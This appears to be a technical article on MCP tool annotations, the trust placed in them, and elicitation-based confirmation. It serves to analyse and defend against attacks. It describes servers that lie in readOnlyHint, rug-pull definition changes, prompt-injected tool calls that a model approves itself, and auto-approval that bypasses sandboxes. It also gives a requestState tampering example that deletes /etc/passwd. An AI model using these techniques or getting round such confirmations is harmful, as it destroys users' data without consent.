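MCP and OpenAI define destructive tools differently. In MCP, `destructiveHint: false` means that the tool performs only additive updates. OpenAI asks for `destructiveHint: true` when a tool can cause outcomes that are irreversible or difficult to reverse. If a document service keeps every past version of a file and lets anyone restore one with a click, a tool that overwrites the file is probably destructive under MCP's definition, because replacing text is not additive. It is not destructive under OpenAI's, because the overwrite is easy to reverse.

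The two tests also give different results for email. Sending a message adds something and erases nothing, so a developer could call it additive and declare `destructiveHint: false`. But nobody can reliably recall a sent email, so sending one is destructive by OpenAI's test. In Sam's case, a conscientious developer could have set `destructiveHint: false` on the tool that would have sent a tax return to a stranger.

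| Operation | Purely additive? | Easy to reverse? | `destructiveHint` under the MCP definition | `destructiveHint` under OpenAI's guide |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Create a draft | Yes | Yes | false | false |
| Send an email | Yes | No | false | true |
| Overwrite a file that has a version history | No | Yes | true | false |
| Delete a file permanently | No | No | true | true |

The example filesystem server follows the stricter reading. It marks `move_file` as destructive, with the explanation that the tool deletes the source file, although a user could normally move the file back. `create_directory` is the only one of the server's four writing tools with `destructiveHint: false`.

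If either test gives true, a developer who is unsure does better to declare true or leave the hint unset. Too much caution will probably just add a confirmation prompt, while wrongly declaring false may remove the only one.

### How developers fill in the hints

The official examples have only recently become complete. Until May 2026, more than a year after the hints entered the specification, only one of the 18 tools in Everything, a server that demonstrates MCP's features, had annotations. That month the project merged *feat(everything): add tool-level annotations to get-annotated-message* (olaservo, 2026), which set all four hints on all 18 tools.

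OpenAI reviews plugins before publishing them, which puts more pressure on developers. Its plugin rules require explicit labels on tools that create, update, delete, post or send, and OpenAI says incorrect or missing labels are a common cause of rejection. In the forum post *Clarification needed on rejection feedback*, a developer quotes a reviewer who wanted annotations "explicitly set to true or false (not null) for every tool", with a justification based on what the tool does. The developer was unsure whether this applied to `idempotentHint`, which OpenAI's reference listed as optional.

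A rule like this makes developers think about each tool, but it also leads them to set hints that have no meaning. OpenAI's own example, `list_projects`, sets `destructiveHint: false` even though the tool is read-only and the hint only applies to tools that aren't.

Software can also fill in hints that the developer did not set. In an example from the documentation of PraisonAI, a framework for building AI agents, a developer declares a tool read-only and non-destructive and does not set the other two hints. The framework then sends all four to the client, including the defaults `idempotentHint: false` and `openWorldHint: true`. The client would have assumed the same defaults if they had been omitted, but it cannot tell which of the values it receives were chosen by the developer.

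### A census of declared hints

Trofimov and Novikov counted what servers declare, using a snapshot of the official MCP registry, a public catalogue, from 27 July 2026. Theaspshot listed 18,688 distinct servers. They excluded 9,454 that had no remote address, because testing those would have meant running other people's programs, and sent a `tools/list` request to each of the other 9,234. Of these, 4,838 returned at least one tool, and nearly all the rest failed to connect. The servers returned 98,291 tools in total, with a median of 11 per server. For each tool, Trofimov and Novikov recorded whether each hint was true, false or absent. They did not call any of the tools.

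One publisher, registered as `io.github.pipeworx-io`, had 44,227 of the tools, or 45.0%, and set all four hints on every one. Trofimov and Novikov therefore give most of their figures twice:

| Share of tools | All 98,291 tools | Without the largest publisher |
| --- | --- | --- |
| No hint declared | 26.0% | 47.2% |
| At least one hint declared | 74.0% | 52.8% |
| All four hints declared | 61.7% | 30.3% |
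| Read-only, non-destructive, idempotent and open-world | 39.9% | 7.3% |
| `destructiveHint` declared on a read-only tool | 52.8% | 26.0% |
| `destructiveHint` declared where it applies | 12.9% | 11.7% |
| Destructive operation declared | 3.1% | 3.2% |

The second column, which leaves out the largest publisher, is the better guide to what developers in general do. With every tool included, the most common combination is read-only, non-destructive, idempotent and open-world, but subtracting one column from the other shows that about four-fifths of the largest publisher's tools have it. Without that publisher, the most common choice is to declare no hints. Setting `readOnlyHint: true` alone would also give a tool the same effective description as declaring all four hints in that combination.

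`destructiveHint`, the field that matters most for confirmation, appears on 65.8% of all tools. On four out of five of those tools, it accompanies `readOnlyHint: true` and has no meaning. It applies to only 12.9% of all tools, and servers declare most of these non-destructive. Only 3.1% of all tools, or about 3,000, are declared destructive, a figure that barely changes when the largest publisher is excluded.

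A host that applies the defaults would reach a very different total, because it would treat every tool without hints as destructive. At least 29% of the tools in the census would then count as destructive, as would at least half of the tools that don't come from the largest publisher. Most of these would count as destructive only because their developers declared no hints.

Developers who use hints often set them differently for different tools. Among servers with several tools and at least one declared hint, 76.7% use more than one combination of hints. However, on the median server that declares any hints, a single combination covers 79.4% of the tools.

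The census leaves out servers that run on the user's own machine. Afsar (2026), in *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, randomly selected 400 of these from npm, a package catalogue for JavaScript, and tried to start each one. Only 195 worked. They offered 2,766 tools, of which 58.8% had no annotations. Developers seem to decide whether to annotate for a whole server rather than for each tool, since 72 servers annotated every tool, 122 annotated none and no server annotated only some.

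Afsar had earlier run the same test on 24 well-known servers and found that only 41.5% of their tools lacked annotations. A survey of popular servers would therefore overstate how common hints are.

### Comparing declarations with code

Neither count shows what the tools do. A tool marked read-only may delete files, and one with no hints may be a harmless calculator. The 3.1% counts declarations, so it can't be used to estimate how many MCP tools are destructive. The counts also give a tool that nobody calls the same weight as one that thousands of people call every day. Servers declare more than half the tools in the census read-only, but a separate analysis by Stein, cited in *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* (2026), found that tools that act on the outside world rose from 27% to 65% of tool usage between November 2024 and February 2026.

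Checking whether hints are accurate requires reading the code. Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *When Neither Side Confirms*, did this for a sample of 1,000 code repositories from the registry. A keyword-based program picked out tools that might be destructive, and two language models then read the code of 366 of them. A tool counted as destructive if some call to it could irreversibly delete or overwrite data, send messages, move money or run arbitrary commands.

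They estimate that 70% of destructive tools have neither a destructive hint nor a confirmation step in the server, and another 20% have only the hint. The split is uncertain because a few repositories with many tools can shift it, and the 95% confidence interval for the 70% figure runs from 43% to 88%. The estimate also partly explains the low figure in the census, because most developers of destructive tools do not declare them as destructive.

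Omitting a hint does little harm in a host that applies the defaults, because the host still treats the tool as destructive. Falsely labelling a destructive tool as read-only or non-destructive is worse. An estimated 5.4% of the destructive tools that the program identified had such a label and belonged to servers that did not ask a person before acting. When Yao and colleagues included destructive tools that the program had missed, the share rose to at least 10.6%.

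Some of these declarations may be neither dishonest nor careless. A developer who marks an email tool as non-destructive because it only adds messages contradicts the study's definition but arguably follows the one in the schema. The study's own labels were open to the same kind of disagreement. When two people checked a sample, they agreed with the models on 51 of the 56 tools they felt sure about. In the other five cases, the models had labelled as destructive an action that the people considered reversible or harmless, such as renaming a project.

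Besides hints, a server provides a written description of each tool, which the model reads when it chooses a tool. *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (2026) compares these descriptions with the tools' code and recommends that clients check the two for consistency before offering a tool to the model. A similar check on hints could catch a tool called `delete_record` that is marked read-only, but it would require access to the code, which the operator of a remote server does not have to share.

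## Why annotations count as untrusted

The maintainers tell clients in three places to distrust annotations, and they word the rule differently each time. The Model Context Protocol *Tools* page states it as a capitalised requirement, the protocol's overview states it as a lower-case principle, and the schema includes it as a comment. The same comment appears in the protocol's *ToolAnnotationsSchema*, a reference page for TypeScript developers.

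| Place | Wording | What it covers |
| --- | --- | --- |
| *Tools* page | "clients MUST consider tool annotations to be untrusted unless they come from trusted servers" | Annotations |
| Overview | "should be considered untrusted, unless obtained from a trusted server" | All descriptions of tool behaviour, with annotations as an example |
| Schema comment | "Clients should never make tool use decisions based on ToolAnnotations received from untrusted servers" | Annotations |

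### What each wording forbids

Only the wording on the *Tools* page has the force that BCP 14 gives to capitalized keywords, but it covers what a client "considers" and doesn't specify any action. A host can display "The server describes this tool as read-only" next to the arguments and still comply, because it does not vouch for the description. If the host skips the confirmation prompt because of the same hint, it has clearly trusted the hint.

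Under the schema comment, clients should not base "tool use decisions" on annotations from untrusted servers. The phrase most naturally means decisions about whether to call a tool and whether to ask the user first, so a host may show such a server's hints but should not act on them. The comment lacks the capitalized keywords that mark formal requirements, but it is the best available guide to what "untrusted" means on the *Tools* page, since both concern the same field.

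The overview principle is the broadest and the hardest to follow because it covers tool descriptions, which the model has to read to choose a tool. The Model Context Protocol schema page suggests that clients use these descriptions to improve the model's understanding. If a host withheld every untrusted description, the model would have to guess from tool names. In practice, hosts therefore have to let the model read the descriptions and apply safeguards after it chooses a tool but before the call is made.

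### The debate on pull request 185

Basil Hosmer of Anthropic wrote pull request 185, the proposed change to the specification that added annotations to MCP, according to *MCP Tool Annotations* (Dumbris, 2026). The Model Context Protocol blog post on tool annotations quotes the review of that pull request.

Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, thought the information would be very useful if clients could trust it, but wondered "how a client makes use of this flag knowing that it's not trustable". Hosmer, who wrote the proposal, went further and argued that clients should ignore every annotation from an untrusted server, "even `title`", and especially those that describe what a tool does.

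According to the blog post, the maintainers compromised by calling every annotation a hint, requiring clients to distrust hints by default, and letting clients judge "how much weight" a particular server's hints deserve. That phrase implies degrees of trust, so it is looser than the schema comment, whose "never" rules out trusting an untrusted server's hints at all.

The maintainers' view of `title` has also softened. In the blog post, they treat a title as useful even from an untrusted server, since the worst outcome is a bad display name. But a host may show that name in a confirmation prompt, and a user who sees "Save draft" may approve a tool that deletes the draft. Ignoring `annotations.title` would not help much, because a dishonest server also chooses the tool's `name` and top-level `title`. A host can protect the user better by identifying the server and showing the arguments of the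 tool call.

### An honest server and a lying one

Suppose that two servers each offer a tool for tidying a customer database, and both send this entry, shown here without its description and input schema:

```json
{
  "name": "delete_duplicates",
  "annotations": { "readOnlyHint": true }
}
```

If the server's hint is accurate, the tool is just poorly named. It finds duplicate records and lists them so the user can delete them later. If the hint is false, the tool deletes records as soon as the call arrives.

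The client receives identical text from both. The entry has no signature and nobody outside the server has checked it, as gyorgy, in *MCP annotations are a UX layer, not a security layer*, points out, so a careful developer and a liar look the same to the protocol. A host that always asks before a call that may change data would get these results:

| Host's policy | Honest server | Lying server |
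| --- | --- | --- |
| Believe the hint | No prompt, no harm | No prompt, records lost |
| Ignore the hint | One needless prompt | A prompt, which the user can refuse |

A host can't tell from a tool's entry whether the server is honest, so it has to get that information elsewhere. The answer to Spahr-Summers's question is therefore that a hint is useful to a client that already has grounds to trust the server. For any other client, `readOnlyHint: true` is a claim that a dishonest server could make just as easily as an honest one.

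A host can follow Hosmer's advice to ignore such hints simply by deleting the `annotations` field. The cautious defaults then apply to `delete_duplicates`, as if the server had declared nothing. Discarding hints can therefore make a tool look riskier but never safer.

Treating annotations as untrusted puts honest developers at a disadvantage. Annotating a harmless tool doesn't benefit its developer until a host has some reason to trust the server, and a host that never trusts any server gives developers no reason to annotate at all.

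### Why a reassuring hint is more dangerous than a warning

The blog post gives an example of what a client might do with each hint. In two cases the client becomes less careful, and in the other two it becomes more careful:

| Declaration | Possible response by the client | Result if the declaration is false |
| --- | --- | --- |
| `readOnlyHint: true` | Skip the confirmation dialog | The tool changes data without asking |
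| `idempotentHint: true` | Retry after a failure | The tool may pay an invoice twice |
| `destructiveHint: true` | Show a warning | The user reads a needless warning |
| `openWorldHint: true` | Check the output for untrusted content | The client does a needless check |

A simple calculation shows how strong the evidence for a read-only hint would have to be. Let *p* be the chance that a call to a tool declared read-only does damage, *L* the size of the loss, *q* the chance that the user refuses a damaging call when asked, and *c* the cost of a prompt. The prompt is worth showing when

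*pqL* > *c*, or equivalently *p* > *c* / (*qL*).

Suppose answering a prompt takes five seconds, repairing the database takes 20 hours (72,000 seconds), and users catch half of all damaging calls. Then *c* / (*qL*) is 5 / 36,000, or 1 in 7,200. The host should skip the prompt only if it expects fewer than one call in 7,200 to do damage. These numbers are invented, but any large loss gives a similarly low threshold.

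For an unknown server, *p* also depends on how hosts behave. A dishonest operator would have little reason to fake `readOnlyHint` if no host acted on it, but once hosts skip prompts because of it, a false hint lets the operator's tools run without anyone reviewing the calls. A low rate of false hints in today's servers would therefore be weak evidence that hosts could safely trust hints from unknown servers.

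Believing a warning carries less risk, so a host might reasonably trust an unknown server that declares its own tool destructive. Read literally, the schema comment forbids even this, because adding a confirmation prompt is a tool use decision. A host that applies the defaults avoids the conflict, since it already treats the tool as destructive. But clients vary in how strictly they apply the defaults, according to the blog post. If a host asks for confirmation only when a tool is explicitly declared destructive, believing the warning would protect its users better than ignoring it.

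One objection to extra warnings is that people who see too many prompts may stop reading them, which lowers *q* for the prompts that matter. If users caught only 5% of damaging calls instead of half, the threshold in the example would rise from 1 in 7,200 to 1 in 720. A dishonest server could exploit this by marking harmless tools as destructive until the user clicks Allow out of habit.

The asymmetry does have limits, and this objection is a good reason for hosts to reduce the number of prompts, but not to let unknown servers decide which prompts to remove. A host can cut prompts by letting users approve particular tools, identifying servers it has grounds to trust, or limiting the damage a tool can do.

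### Who counts as a trusted server

The rule makes an exception for trusted servers, so how much it requires depends on which servers count as trusted. The maintainers don't define "trusted server" on any of the three pages or specify whether the user, the host's developer or a company's administrator decides which servers qualify.

According to the blog post, a company that runs its own MCP servers behind a login can base policy on their annotations, while annotations from a random server on the internet are "informational at best". Most servers fall somewhere between these two cases. For example, a user might have found a server in a public catalogue, read a few good reviews and connected it to an email account.

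The maintainers report in the same post that most clients trust any server the user has installed. This is partly reasonable, because a malicious server running on the user's computer may be able to delete files as soon as it starts, without waiting for a tool call. Believing its hints therefore adds little danger.

But that argument doesn't work for a remote server, which may have no access to the user's data except through tool calls. It also conflicts with the MUST on the *Tools* page, which makes sense only if a host can connect to a server without trusting it. A client receives annotations only from servers that somebody has connected to the host, so if connecting a server were enough to make it trusted, the rule would almost never apply.

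A curated registry could supply some of the missing evidence. Stacklok's *Tool annotations are becoming the risk vocabulary for agentic systems* proposes that its maintainers inspect each server's source code and confirm that the annotations match. A host could then rely on the registry's check instead of the developer's word. This would work best when users download the exact version the reviewers read, because the operator of a remote server can publish one version of the code and run another.

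Trust in a server may not extend to every tool it offers. Some programs, often called gateways, collect tools from several servers and present them as one list. A company might trust its own gateway completely even though unknown third parties wrote the annotations on half the tools. The gateway is a trusted server and it sends those annotations, but the gateway's operator may never have checked them.

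### Honest servers that are wrong

Even an honest server can supply wrong annotations. A developer may copy them from another tool, misread a definition, or add a delete option in a later version and forget to update the hint. MCProspero's *RFC 001* (2026) cites a study of 10,240 MCP servers in which about 13% had significant mismatches between their written descriptions and their code. The study's figure is for descriptions rather than hints, and a mismatch does not show that anyone meant to deceive, but it suggests that careless metadata is common.

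The schema comment calls all annotations hints that may not describe the tool faithfully, whoever runs the server. Its ban on basing tool use decisions on them applies only to untrusted servers. A client may therefore rely on a trusted server's hints and still be misled. A sensible test of a company's internal server covers whether anyone checks the annotations when the code changes, as well as whether the team that runs it means well.

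### Definitions that change after approval

A tool's annotations can also be accurate when the user approves the tool and inaccurate an hour later. Two mechanisms help the client track such changes.

A server can notify the client of a change to its tool list only if the server has declared support for notifications and the client has opened a stream to receive them. Even then, sending a notification is recommended (SHOULD), not required. The example notification on the *Tools* page contains no details, so the client has to request the list again and work out what changed.

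The server also gives every tool list a lifetime in a field called `ttlMs`. Model Context Protocol's *Caching* (2026) says the client SHOULD treat the list as fresh for that many milliseconds, although the server MAY change its tools sooner. McCaffrey (2026) proposed the field in *SEP-2549*, partly because many clients and servers struggle to keep open the long-lived connections that notifications need.

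Suppose that the honest server changes hands, and the new operator wants `delete_duplicates` to delete records:

- **10:00:** The client fetches the tool list, with `readOnlyHint: true` and a lifetime of 300,000 milliseconds, or five minutes. The user approves all future calls to the tool.
- **10:02:** The operator installs the new code and changes the hint to false. The client has no notification stream open.
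- **10:04:** The model calls the tool. The client's copy of the list is still fresh, so it sends the call without checking, and the server deletes the records.
- **10:05:** The list expires. The next time the client needs it, it fetches the new hint, but the host still has the user's approval on file.

Neither the *Caching* page nor the *Tools* page requires the host to ask the user again. In the security discussion, McCaffrey considers a malicious server that sets an excessively long lifetime and judges the risk minimal because clients can ignore the value or fetch the list early, but does not address approvals. The closest text is a principle in the overview, written with a lower-case "must", that users must consent to and understand all operations. Someone who approved a read-only tool has not consented to or understood a deletion, so the principle supports asking again. However, a host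 that never asks again would not break any capitalised requirement on either page.

Some clients don't react to notifications at all. In *MCP: notifications/tools/list_changed not acted on mid-session*, a post on the forum of the code editor Cursor, a user describes a test server that starts with one tool, adds another and notifies the client. The new tool remained unavailable until the session restarted. The user reports the same behaviour in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Such a client keeps showing the old definition while the server runs its current code.

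Security companies call this change a rug pull when it is deliberate. SecureW2's *MCP Rug Pull Attacks* recommends the Enhanced Tool Definition Interface (ETDI), a proposed addition to MCP. Developers would cryptographically sign each tool definition and issue a new signed version for any change, which would trigger a new request for approval. *ETDI concepts* describes this as a layer that leaves the core protocol largely unchanged.

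Without signatures, a host can still get part of the benefit by saving a tool's definition when the user approves the tool, comparing it with each new list, and asking again if they differ. Dumbris suggests something similar for a proxy, a program between the host and its servers that could flag annotations that change between sessions. Deciding which changes matter is difficult. A switch from read-only to destructive obviously does. A reworded description might only fix a spelling mistake, but MCProspero notes that changing the words alone can change how the model uses a tool.

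Comparing a tool's definition with a saved copy and checking its signature both detect changes to the definition. If the server's operator installs new code but leaves `readOnlyHint: true` in place, the saved copy still matches and any signature is still valid. The server can therefore change its behaviour without either check detecting it, so the host needs a safeguard that doesn't depend on the definition.

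### Hints and enforcement

In the blog post, the maintainers distinguish hints, which inform decisions, from contracts, which enforce them. They argue that if an annotation's value depends on its being true, it belongs in the authorization layer, the transport or the runtime. `readOnlyHint` is hard to justify as a hint under this test, because skipping a confirmation prompt is safe only if the hint is true.

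Enforcement stops an action whatever the server declares. Which kind is available depends on where the tool runs and whose data it touches:

- **A server on the user's computer.** The host can run it in a sandbox, a restricted environment that limits which files it can open. If the customer database is a local file that the sandbox makes read-only, `delete_duplicates` fails on the lying server and works normally on the honest one. Network controls can also stop the server from sending the records elsewhere.
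- **A remote server that works on an account held with another company.** A sandbox on the user's computer has no effect on it. The user can instead give it an access token that allows reading and nothing else, so the company that holds the account refuses the deletion.
- **A remote server that holds the data itself.** The user has no technical means of stopping the operator from deleting records. A confirmation prompt can withhold a particular call, and a separate backup can limit the loss.

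According to *MCP Tool Annotations as Risk Vocabulary* (2026), OpenAI's coding agent Codex relies on an operating-system sandbox and a set of rules for security, and uses annotations mainly to spare the user needless prompts.

Researchers are also trying to replace the server's description of a tool with one the host can verify. In *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents*, Adam, Lu and colleagues combine automated code analysis with sandboxing. The analysis identifies a tool's effects, such as network access, and the sandbox checks the tool's actions against a policy while it runs. The analysis needs the tool's code, so it suits downloaded tools better than remote ones.

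Enforcement also makes hints more useful, because believing a false one does less harm. In the earlier calculation, a prompt was worth showing if more than one call in 7,200 would do damage. If a sandbox limited the worst loss to a minute's work, the same prompt would be worth showing only if more than one call in six did damage, so the host could accept a read-only hint on much weaker evidence.

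## How a server asks the user a question through the client

Sandboxes and read-only tokens limit the damage a server can do, but they don't confirm that the user wants a particular change. Sometimes the server is the first program that has enough information to ask. Partway through a call, it may detect that a query would delete 4,000 records or that the model left out a required field. In such cases, the server can use MCP's elicitation feature to request information or consent. The client relays the request to the user and returns the answer to the server.

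Elicitation has two modes. In form mode, the user fills in a few fields inside the host. In URL mode, which suits passwords and payments, the user opens a web address outside the host.

### A call to delete three files

Sam asks an assistant to clear out old drafts of a plan. The model picks two drafts but also the finished version, and the client sends this call to a file server:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
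  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {
        "elicitation": { "form": {} }
      }
    },
    "name": "delete_files",
    "arguments": {
      "paths": ["plan-v1.txt", "plan-v2.txt", "plan-final.txt"]
    }
  }
}
```

The `elicitation` entry declares that the client can handle forms. According to the Model Context Protocol *Elicitation* page, a client that supports elicitation MUST declare it on each request, and an empty `elicitation` object means that the client supports form mode only. If the client doesn't declare it, the server MUST NOT ask the user, and the safe response to a deletion request is to refuse it. The entry describes what the software can do, so it is not evidence that anyone is at the screen.

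The server deletes nothing yet. It replies with an input-required result:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "input_required",
    "inputRequests": {
      "confirm_delete": {
        "method": "elicitation/create",
        "params": {
          "mode": "form",
          "message": "Permanently delete plan-v1.txt, plan-v2.txt and plan-final.txt?",
          "requestedSchema": {
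            "type": "object",
            "properties": {
              "confirmed": { "type": "boolean", "title": "Yes, delete these files" }
            },
            "required": ["confirmed"]
          }
        }
      }
    },
    "requestState": "opaque-protected-string"
  }
}
```

This reply ends the original request. `inputRequests` can hold several questions, each under a key that the server chooses. `requestState` contains whatever the server needs in order to resume, and the client has to return it unchanged without trying to interpret it. The host might display the question like this:

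```text
local-files asks:
Permanently delete plan-v1.txt, plan-v2.txt and plan-final.txt?
[ ] Yes, delete these files
[Submit]  [Decline]  [Cancel]
```

Sam now has a chance to notice the finished plan. If Sam really does want all three files gone, ticks the box and submits the form, the client sends the call again with a new ID. This copy omits the `_meta` block, which every request still needs:

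```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 8,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "delete_files",
    "arguments": {
      "paths": ["plan-v1.txt", "plan-v2.txt", "plan-final.txt"]
    },
    "inputResponses": {
      "confirm_delete": {
        "action": "accept",
        "content": { "confirmed": true }
      }
    },
    "requestState": "opaque-protected-string"
  }
}
```

The server deletes the files and returns an ordinary result with `resultType` set to `complete`.

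Sending the whole call twice solves a practical problem for remote servers. A popular service runs on many machines, and a user may take hours to answer. Until this revision, the server held a connection open while it waited, and the answer could arrive at a machine that had no record of the question. Roth, McCaffrey and Zimmerman (2026) report in *Multi Round-Trip Requests*, the proposal behind the new exchange, that many remote servers had barely adopted elicitation for this reason. Now the second request contains everything needed to finish the call, so any machine can process it. Supabase had wanted elicitation for some time, but its server keeps no state between requests, according to the Model Context Protocol release announcement.

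The same exchange can run for several rounds. In an example from Roth and colleagues, the model tries to mark a bug as resolved, and the server asks how. The user picks "Duplicate", which makes another field required, so the server asks which bug is the original. The server puts the first answer in `requestState` so the user doesn't have to give it again.

### Accept, decline and cancel

A client can return three actions. For `delete_files`, they should lead to these outcomes:

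| What Sam does | What the client returns | What the server should do |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Ticks the box and submits | `accept`, with `confirmed: true` | Delete the three files |
| Submits with the box empty | `accept`, with `confirmed: false` | Keep the files |
| Clicks Decline | `decline` | Keep the files and perhaps offer to archive them |
| Closes the dialog or presses Escape | `cancel` | Keep the files and perhaps ask again later |
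| Never answers | Nothing | Keep the files |

The second row is easy to get wrong. `accept` means the user submitted the form, whatever the form contains, so a server that checks only the action would delete the files against Sam's wishes. django-stateless-mcp's *Recipe* (2026), a guide for developers using the Django web framework, recommends treating anything except an explicit accept as a no. Its sample code also checks that the submitted value is true.

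Asking again is more reasonable after a `cancel`, which only dismisses the question, than after a `decline`, which is a decision. However, the server MAY keep returning input-required results until it has what it needs, and the specification sets no limit on the number of rounds. Model Context Protocol's *Multi-round-trip requests*, a guide to the official Python SDK, describes a default cap of ten rounds, after which the call fails. The cap applies to each call separately, so it does little against a server that asks the user the same unwelcome question on every new call.

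### What a form can contain

The server describes its form with a small subset of JSON Schema. A form is a flat list of fields, with no nesting, and each field has one of these types:

- **Text**, with optional length limits and a format such as an email address or a date.
- **A number**, with an optional minimum and maximum.
- **True or false**.
- **A choice from a list**, either a single option or several.

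The limits make it easy for any host to draw the form and check the answers. They still leave room for a better question than the one Sam received. The server could list the three files as options and let Sam select the ones to delete:

```json
"files": {
  "type": "array",
  "title": "Files to delete",
  "items": {
    "type": "string",
    "enum": ["plan-v1.txt", "plan-v2.txt", "plan-final.txt"]
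  },
  "default": []
}
```

Sam could then correct the model's mistake instead of refusing the whole call. The arguments in the second request would still name all three files, so the server would have to follow the selection in Sam's answer.

Any field can have a default, and clients that support defaults SHOULD fill it in before the user sees the form. This is convenient for a country or a date, but it can let a user submit a confirmation without making a decision. If the server sets `confirmed` to true by default, the box is already ticked, and the server gets the same reply whether Sam considered the question or just clicked Submit.

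A pre-ticked box is perhaps no worse than an Allow button when the form asks only one short question, since either takes one click. It is riskier when the confirmation shares a form with other fields. Sam might type a name for an archive folder and submit the form without noticing a ticked box below it for deleting the originals.

The MCP specification doesn't prohibit a pre-filled yes, although its true-or-false example defaults to false. Server developers can avoid the problem by omitting the default. A host can also leave such boxes empty, because filling in defaults is only a SHOULD and protecting a confirmation is a good reason to depart from it.

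### What the client owes the user

The duties on clients are stricter here than for tool calls, where all the capitalised clauses on confirmation use SHOULD. For a form, the client MUST:

- have an interface that "makes it clear which server is requesting information"
- respect the user's privacy and offer clear ways to decline and cancel
- let the user review and change the answers before sending them

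Clients SHOULD also make clear what information the server is requesting and why. Cloudflare's *Agents can respond to MCP elicitation requests* (2026) describes a flow in which the agent shows the user which server sent the request, the reason for it and the input requested. The user can then submit, decline or cancel.

Naming the server matters because the server writes the rest of the question. A weather server could send a form headed "Your bank needs to confirm your details", and the host's label would be the only sign that the form did not come from the bank. Letting users change answers matters most when the host drafts them, such as when the model fills in an address from the conversation. Without a review, the user might send the server information it doesn't need.

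The rules are therefore stricter for a form than for the call that led to it. A host may hide the `paths` argument of `delete_files` if it has a reason to, but it must always show Sam the answers in the form.

Servers MUST NOT use a form to request secrets that grant access or authorise transactions, such as passwords, API keys, access tokens or payment credentials, because the answers pass through the client and could end up in its logs or in the model's context. They have to use URL mode for these instead. A server may still use a form to ask for a name or an email address, which the user can decline to give.

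A dishonest developer can ignore this rule. The *Elicitation* page does not require clients to block a form with a field called "password", and a simple filter would miss a field called "recovery phrase". Users are safest if they treat any form with a field for a secret as a warning sign.

### Questions only in reply to a request

Model Context Protocol's *Require Server requests to be associated with a Client request* (2026), known as SEP-2260, allows a server to ask the user a question (elicitation) only while it is processing a client's request. Earlier text only recommended this. The proposal's example of a prohibited design is a background task that wakes every 60 seconds and sends a request of its own.

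SEP-2260 was meant to simplify connections, but it also argued that users would understand why a question had appeared, and that clients could better judge whether to answer if they knew which operation the question served. The rule required little change to existing projects. A search of GitHub found only one project that broke it, a contrived case belonging to the proposal's own author.

The current revision builds the rule into the message format. The Model Context Protocol page on message patterns says that servers MUST NOT initiate requests, so a server can ask a question only in a reply. Model Context Protocol's *Multi Round-Trip Requests* (2026) allows this only in replies to requests to call a tool, fetch a prompt or read a resource.

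In their post on the release candidate, the Model Context Protocol maintainers promise that "A user is never prompted out of nowhere", because every question traces back to something users "(or their agent)" started. The words in brackets weaken the promise considerably, because if injected text leads the model to call a tool, the resulting question may completely surprise the user.

The rule also restricts when a server can ask the user a question, but not what it can ask. Roth and colleagues' proposal includes an example, which they call contrived, where `get_weather` responds to a request about New York by asking for the user's GitHub username. SEP-2260 doesn't forbid this. A host can make the mismatch obvious by showing the original call next to the question.

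### Which mistakes a server's question can catch

The question reaches the user through a different route from the model's output. If the server builds its message from the arguments it is about to act on, a model that chose the wrong files can't hide them from Sam, even if the model has described the task as routine tidying. The server's question and a host prompt that shows all inputs have different strengths:

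| Problem | Host prompt with all inputs | Question from the server |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The model picks the wrong file | Can catch it | Can catch it |
| Injected text picks the files | Can catch it | Can catch it |
| A query matches far more records than expected | Unlikely to catch it | Can catch it, because the server can count the records |
| An argument contains confidential text | Can stop it | Too late, because the server has the text |
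| The server conceals what its tool does | Can't catch it | Can't catch it |

The third row shows the best argument for elicitation. Unlike an annotation, which is the same for every call, a server's question can depend on the query. The server can answer a harmless query immediately and ask the user only about a deletion. A host on its own would have to prompt more often to be safe. The server's questions can also include facts that the host doesn't have, such as a price or the number of records.

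The server's message still has to be specific. The release candidate post's example message, "Delete 3 files?", would give Sam no reason to stop, and neither would a prompt that shows only the tool's name. A server should also avoid copying free text from the model into its message. If `delete_files` had a `reason` argument and the server displayed it, an attacker who controlled the model could write part of the confirmation.

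All of this assumes an honest server. A dishonest server already has the tool's arguments when it asks, so it can delete the files first, describe the deletion as a backup, or skip the question. *Recipe* tells developers that annotations are hints and "this elicitation is the enforcement". This is fair when a server is restraining a model, but users get no comparable protection against the server.

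### Answers that no person gave

An `accept` reply is supposed to mean "User explicitly approved and submitted with data". But the client writes the entire reply, and no field shows who approved it. *Multi Round-Trip Requests* describes the client as gathering input "from the user or other sources".

Software can easily answer in the user's place. The Python SDK runs a function written by the client developer whenever a question arrives. In the guide's example, this function always accepts and returns the region `eu-west-1`, without showing the user anything. The guide says a real application would put its user interface there, but the code works without one.

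Some hosts let users automate responses to elicitations. According to django-stateless-mcp, Claude Code users can set up hooks that do this. *MCP Server Elicitations in Codex CLI* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a Codex setting that turns off approvals and the sandbox and also approves every elicitation without asking the user. OpenAI's *Configuration Reference* lists MCP elicitations among the kinds of prompt that users can have Codex reject automatically. Rejecting every elicitation may block useful work, but it can't cause a deletion that requires approval through one.

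A person who writes a hook has agreed to a policy in advance, but not to deleting `plan-final.txt`. Letting the model answer is worse, because the model that chose the wrong files would confirm its own choice, and injected text that caused the call could also make the model approve it. A second model might catch some errors, but its approval would still not be a human decision. In each case, the server receives the same `accept` as it would if Sam had approved.

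### Protecting requestState

The client holds `requestState` between the two requests, so the *Multi Round-Trip Requests* page says servers MUST treat it as input an attacker controls. If it affects authorisation, access to resources or business logic, the server MUST protect it against changes and reject any value that fails the check. The server can use, for example, an HMAC, which is a code that only someone with a secret key can compute, or authenticated encryption, which also hides the contents.

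The string in the release candidate post has no such protection. It is ordinary Base64 and decodes to `{"step":1,"files":["a","b","c"]}`. Körbächer (2026), in *Designing requestState for Multi Round-Trip Requests*, explains how a client could exploit a similar value. The client changes the step from 1 to 2 and replaces the listed files with `/etc/passwd`, a system file. The server then resumes at step 2 as if the user had already consented, and deletes a file the user was never asked about.

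A valid string can also end up on the wrong request. To prevent this, servers SHOULD put three things inside the protected string and check them when it returns:

- the identity of the user, so that another user can't present it
- a short expiry time
- an identifier for the original request, such as the method and a digest (a short fingerprint) of its important arguments

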